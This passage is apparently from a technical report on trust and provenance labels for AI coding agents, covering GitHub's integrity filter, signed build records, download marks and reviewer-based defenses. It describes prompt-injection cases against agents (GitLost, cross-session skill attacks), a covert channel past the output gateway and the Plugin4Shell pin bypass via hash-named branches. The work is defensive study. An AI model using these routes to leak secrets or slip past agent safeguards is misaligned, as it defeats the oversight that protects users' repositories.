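GitHub and OpenAI have proposed adding standard labels to the Model Context Protocol. According to a summary in *SEP-1862*, the proposal would label results that are private, sensitive, possibly malicious or from the outside world, and set rules for carrying these labels into later requests and sessions. It could also label each item in a list of search results separately, which would help when a maintainer's comment and a stranger's comment arrive together. The protocol's index still listed the proposal as a draft in July 2026.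 Without a standard, labels in `_meta` work mainly where one organization controls both the client and the server, because other clients won't recognize them.

### GitHub's filter for agentic workflows

GitHub Agentic Workflows, which run agents as automated jobs on a repository, already enforce a kind of integrity label. A gateway between the agent and GitHub gives each issue, comment and pull request a trust level and removes anything below a set minimum before the agent sees it. GitHub defines five levels:

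| Level | What qualifies |
|---|---|
| merged | Merged pull requests and commits on the default branch, whoever wrote them |
| approved | Content from owners, members, collaborators and trusted bots, and everything in private repositories |
| unapproved | Content from other contributors |
| none | Content from people with no history in the project |
| blocked | Content from accounts that the maintainers have blocked |

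This filter does well on several of the five tests. It assigns levels from GitHub's records of who wrote or merged something. GitHub's *Under the hood* (2026) explains that the agent and the gateway run in separate containers, so the agent can't easily forge these levels. Setting the minimum level takes one line of configuration. GitHub's *Weekly Update* (2026) describes a March release that made "approved" the default for workflows on public repositories. That default replaced an automatic version of Lockdown mode, which GitHub (2025) had introduced in its MCP server to restrict content from untrusted contributors.

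For the bug-report example, though, the default filters too much. It hides the stranger's whole issue from the agent, including the description of the crash as well as the injection. If the workflow's configuration allows it, a maintainer can raise the issue to "approved" by adding a particular tag. The approval then covers the whole issue, including any injection the maintainer overlooked. The issue's author can also edit the text afterwards, and GitHub's documentation mentions no rule that cancels the approval if they do. If the approval were tied to a hash of the text, an edit would invalidate it.

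A trust filter also doesn't stop secrets from leaking. In July 2026, the security firm Noma disclosed GitLost, a flaw in these workflows. SiliconANGLE's *‘GitLost’ vulnerability let GitHub’s AI workflows leak private repositories* (2026) reports that an outsider could obtain data from private repositories by posting one crafted issue in a public one. GitHub Next's undated post *Control what your agentic workflows see with integrity filtering* had acknowledged that the gateway tracked secrecy but didn't enforce it, so it couldn't prevent leaks between repositories.

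That has since changed, at least in part. A code change that GitHub merged on July 12 refers to default protections against data flowing from private to public places. The change lets a workflow's author turn off all of these protections or exempt particular servers from one of them, but strict mode doesn't allow turning them all off. The gateway's documentation, GitHub's *gh aw mcpg*, describes separate policies for servers that an agent reads from and servers that it writes to.

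Under GitHub's *Safe Outputs MCP Gateway Specification*, a working draft from October 2026, agents don't write to GitHub directly. The agent declares the operations it wants, and a separate job with its own permissions carries them out. GitHub excludes covert channels from its threat model, so the agent could still encode a secret in the operations it declares.

### Is a private repository trustworthy?

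GitHub's MCP server labels everything in a public repository (untrusted, public) and everything in a private one (trusted, private). Under this convention, the context label depends only on which kinds of repository the agent has read:

| What the agent has read | Context label |
|---|---|
| Only public repositories | untrusted, public |
| Only private repositories | trusted, private |
| Both | untrusted, private |

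A policy that stops an (untrusted, private) agent from posting in public acts only when a session mixes public and private repositories. It is a sensible place to start because it would have stopped the leak that Invariant Labs demonstrated and doesn't interrupt work within one kind of repository.

But outsiders' text also gets into private repositories, through customers' bug reports, copies of open-source libraries and files written by agents that had read public issues. The Miasma worm committed itself to any repository its victims could write to. If an injection is in a private repository, the context label stays trusted, and the Teams policy above would let the agent send private data to any channel.

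For public projects the convention is too strict, because it also covers merged code, which the workflow filter puts at its highest level.

CapScope, by contrast, fixes an agent's permissions before the agent reads any file, so it doesn't need to trust the repository. This works for permissions, but a labeling scheme that treated the repository as untrusted would mark every coding session untrusted as soon as the agent opened a file, and the label would no longer distinguish between sessions.

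It would be better to track a file's confidentiality separately from its trustworthiness. A repository's privacy setting determines who may read the file, but trust in the file should depend on who approved that exact version, whether the repository is public or private.

### Labels assigned by a model

*Taming Various Privilege Escalation in LLM-Based Agent Systems* (Ji, Wu and colleagues, 2026) presents SEAGENT, a system that uses tool labels to block dangerous sequences of tool calls. Because labeling tools by hand is tedious, a model proposes the labels and people correct them. The labels describe what each tool acts on, whether it reads, writes or executes, how sensitive the operation is, whether its results are trustworthy and whether they are personal. Fixed rules then use these labels to decide what to block. One rule stops an agent that has received unfiltered text from an external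 tool from writing or executing anything of moderate or high sensitivity.

With the corrected labels, no attack succeeded on AgentDojo, compared with 39% against an unprotected agent. None succeeded on InjecAgent, a benchmark with 80 labeled tools, either. This shows that the rules work when the labels are right, but it's weaker evidence about labels that nobody has corrected.

In a test on harmless tasks, SEAGENT raised two false alarms. Both times, the agent had looked something up on Wikipedia before trying to record health data or book an appointment. Ji and colleagues say that labeling the Wikipedia tool as trusted would prevent these alarms. But anyone can edit Wikipedia, so that one change would also let through an injection placed there.

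SEAGENT gives each tool fixed labels, which doesn't suit a shell. Labels based on what each command opened, as in FLOWSH, work better there.

### Who wrote a file and what influenced it

The most common marks on finished files record that an agent took part, which is separate from whether an untrusted source influenced the file:

| | No untrusted influence | Untrusted influence |
|---|---|---|
| An agent wrote it | A function renamed at the developer's request | The fix for the stranger's bug report |
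| A person wrote it | The developer's own code | A snippet the developer copied from the issue |

A system that bases trust on authorship can trust content too much or too little. GitHub Next's post says that the workflow filter has a built-in list of trusted bots, including Copilot, and raises whatever they write to "approved". If Copilot summarized the stranger's issue in a comment and copied the injection into it, the comment would get a higher trust level than the issue.

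Projects can attach several kinds of marks to commits, builds and downloads:

| Mark | Who assigns it | Can a hijacked agent forge or remove it? | Does it survive copying? | What checks it? |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Line in a commit message | Usually the agent | Yes | With the commit, but a squash merge may drop it | Usually nothing |
| Git note | Any tool or person with write access | Yes, with that access | Not in an ordinary clone | Whatever the team builds |
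| Record of agent-written lines | The editor or agent software | Often, if it can write to the records | Only if tools update it after edits | Mostly viewers for people |
| Signed build record | The build service | Not if the signing key is out of reach | Yes, matched by the file's hash | A verifier, if the recipient runs one |
| Download mark | The browser or mail program | Yes, with the user's permissions | Sometimes | The operating system and some applications |

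The first three take little effort and are mainly useful for bookkeeping. A Git trailer is a line in the commit message, so a signature on the commit covers it. A Git note is a separate record attached to a commit's hash, so a reviewer can add information later without changing the commit. However, Git doesn't fetch or push notes by default, and a rebase, which replaces old commits with new ones, leaves the notes on the old commits unless someone has configured Git to copy them.

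Line-level formats are more detailed. Agent Trace, an open format that the company behind Cursor published in early 2026, records whether a person or a model wrote each range of lines and can link the range to the conversation that produced it. Git AI, an open-source tool, keeps similar records in Git notes. For taint tracking, a reviewer could use the link to look up what the agent had read.

### Signed build records

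in-toto and SLSA (Supply-chain Levels for Software Artifacts) provide a much stronger way to attach information to a file. in-toto defines a signed statement in three parts: the names and hashes of the files it covers, the type of claim, and the claim itself. SLSA defines one such claim, which records what built a file, from which source and with which parameters. At SLSA's third build level, the build service signs the record and keeps the key away from the project's own build steps, so a script that a hijacked agent has edited can't forge it.

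A valid record shows where a file came from, but the file may still be harmful. If a maintainer merges a patch with a backdoor, the build service will sign an accurate record that it built the program from the approved source. The record may also be incomplete, because SLSA doesn't require it to list all of the build's dependencies. In a case like Cline's, a poisoned cache could affect a release without appearing in its record.

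in-toto also allows a team to define claims of its own. A claim could list the outside text that an agent had read before it wrote a file, which is what an integrity label needs. This would be fairly new for agents. Among the 71 works in their survey, Wang and colleagues found little reporting of agent records that resist tampering or carry a verifiable signature.

### Download marks

Desktop operating systems have used a simple taint label for about two decades. On Windows, browsers attach a Mark of the Web to each downloaded file. Microsoft Office opens marked documents in a restricted view, and Windows may warn the user before running a marked program. macOS has a similar quarantine mark. Unlike the marks on commits, these labels record that a file came from outside, regardless of who wrote it.

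Marks on downloaded files have several weaknesses that a label for agents would share. The program that saves a file has to add the mark, and command-line tools such as `curl` and `git` normally don't. Windows keeps the mark in a part of the file that many USB drives can't store. An archive program has to copy the mark to every file it unpacks, and 7-Zip failed to do this for some archives inside other archives. Attackers exploited that flaw against Ukrainian organizations before 7-Zip fixed it in November 2024. Users can also remove a mark, and so can any program that runs with their permissions, including a coding agent.

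A missing mark is therefore weak evidence that a file is safe. Both systems still treat unmarked files more leniently than marked ones, because being equally strict with both would interrupt people constantly. A repository can be stricter than a desktop because changes already go through a review, and teams can send any file without a record there.

### A pin that nobody checked

A hash also protects a file only if something checks the file against it. In September 2026, the firm Air Security published Plugin4Shell, a flaw that affected Claude Code, Codex, GitHub Copilot and Gemini CLI. Constantin (2026) explains in *Plugin4Shell* that plugin marketplaces for these agents pin each plugin to the hash of a reviewed commit. The agents requested that commit but never verified that they had received it.

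Git allows a branch to have the same name as a commit hash, and it chooses the branch when a name matches both. Whoever controlled a plugin's repository could create a branch named after the reviewed commit's hash, put different code in it and make it the default branch. The agent then installed that code but reported installing the pinned version. Gemini CLI fetched the right commit first, but an attacker could divert the next step with a branch called `FETCH_HEAD`. The victim didn't have to click anything.

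The repair is a single comparison after the download, roughly:

```
test "$(git rev-parse HEAD)" = "$PINNED_COMMIT" || exit 1
```

By September 21, Anthropic and OpenAI had fixed their agents, but Microsoft had not fixed Copilot. Google decided against a fix because it is retiring Gemini CLI. GitHub's planned lock files for its automation service would avoid this mistake because a mismatched hash would stop a workflow before any of its jobs ran, according to the company's roadmap (GitHub, 2026).

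The same mistake is possible with any label stored apart from its file. If a record lists `parser.py` as approved by a maintainer, the build has to hash the file it is about to use and compare the result with the hash in the record, not just match the file or branch name.

### Showing the next agent where a file came from

Even a correct label may have little effect if a model is left to interpret it. Liao and colleagues tested this with SkillRelayGuard, their defense against the cross-session attacks in SkillRelayBench. It works in three stages:

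1. At the end of a session, a separate model proposes which skills influenced which files. For each link, it has to cite an instruction in the skill, a tool call that carried it out and the resulting change in the file. Ordinary code verifies that the cited evidence exists, then stores the link with the file's hash, outside the agent's reach.
2. When a later agent reads the file, the system adds a note about its origin and a reminder that requests inside the file don't carry the user's authority.
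3. Before certain operations, a reviewing model compares the request with the user's task and the original materials, then gives advice. The agent has to wait for the advice, but it may ignore it.

Across three coding agents, attack success fell from 69.5% to 10.9%, and the share of completed tasks rose from 79.6% to 87.5%. The improvement in completed work makes sense, because many of the attacks also made the user's results wrong. Liao and colleagues then separated the two interventions, using Codex CLI with GPT-5.3-Codex:

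| Defense | Attacks that succeeded | Tasks completed |
|---|---|---|
| None | 77.4% | 85.6% |
| Note about the file's origin | 73.3% | 93.3% |
| Review before the operation | 25.9% | 95.2% |
| Both | 17.4% | 90.4% |

Telling the agent where a file came from hardly reduced the attacks. Most of the reduction came from the reviewer, which could also consult the origin records. This suggests that labels are more useful to a separate reviewer than to the agent doing the task, although the test doesn't show how well the reviewer would have done without the records.

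SkillRelayGuard used 4.3% of the tokens but 40% of the running time, about a minute and a half per case. It can't contain an agent that is already hijacked, because the agent can confirm an operation that the reviewer advised against. To contain such an agent, a policy would have to make the reviewer's refusal binding.

### A minimal scheme for a repository

A team can avoid most of this complexity by using one label, untrusted, and attaching it to whole branches instead of files. Everything on a branch that an agent has written to stays untrusted until a maintainer approves its latest commit. The scheme doesn't need a secrecy label as long as the agent never has access to secrets. It has six steps:

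1. Run the agent in a sandbox with a fresh clone of the repository, no `.env` file and no publishing credentials.
2. Load AGENTS.md, editor settings and hooks only from the last approved commit, and don't let the agent change the loaded copies.
3. When the agent finishes, export its source changes to a branch and delete the rest of the clone.
4. Attach a signed record of what the session read. Treat a missing or invalid record as untrusted.
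5. Run the tests without secrets, and don't let release jobs use any cache that these tests have written.
6. Require a maintainer to approve the exact commit, cancel the approval if anything changes, and have the release job verify the hash before it builds.

For the patch in the bug-report example, the record could look like this:

```
covers:     commit 8f3c… (full hash)
session:    fix-issue-482
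read:       issue 482, written by a non-member
label:      untrusted
signed by:  the agent's harness
```

The harness has to write the record outside the sandbox and sign it with a key the agent can't reach. Reviewers can use the record to see which outside text to compare with the patch. If the issue later turns out to be malicious, the team can also search for every commit it may have influenced.

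Step 3 removes the hook from the example. The line in AGENTS.md might reach the branch as an ordinary change, but no agent loads it as an instruction unless a maintainer approves it. The agent never had the token, so the fixture can't contain it. The patch still needs careful review.

Much of this is available already:

| Part | What exists | What a team has to build |
|---|---|---|
| Sandbox without secrets | Containers and virtual machines | A setup that still lets the project's tests run |
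| Approved instructions and settings | Git can supply any earlier version of a file | A wrapper that loads these versions and protects them |
| Export of source changes | Git patches and branches | A short script that refuses hooks and unexpected files |
| Record of what the session read | in-toto statements and signing tools | The claim format, and a harness that collects the list |
| Tests without secrets | Permission settings on most build services | Separate caches for untrusted branches and releases |
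| Approval of the exact commit | Protected branches, required reviewers and cancellation of outdated approvals | A list of sensitive files that need a particular owner's approval |
| Final check | Hash comparison and SLSA verifiers | A release step that stops when a hash or approval doesn't match |

The agent should push from its own account, without the right to approve changes or alter the branch rules. A secret scanner also helps in case someone puts a credential in the sandbox by mistake. Most users can override the blocks that GitHub's own scanner puts on tool calls, so the agent shouldn't be allowed to override them.

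The list of what a session read is the hardest part to build, because a shell command can fetch text from anywhere. A team can start without this list by labeling every agent branch untrusted. Later, it can add a monitor such as FLOWSH and allow a lighter review when the record shows that a session read only the developer's request and approved files.
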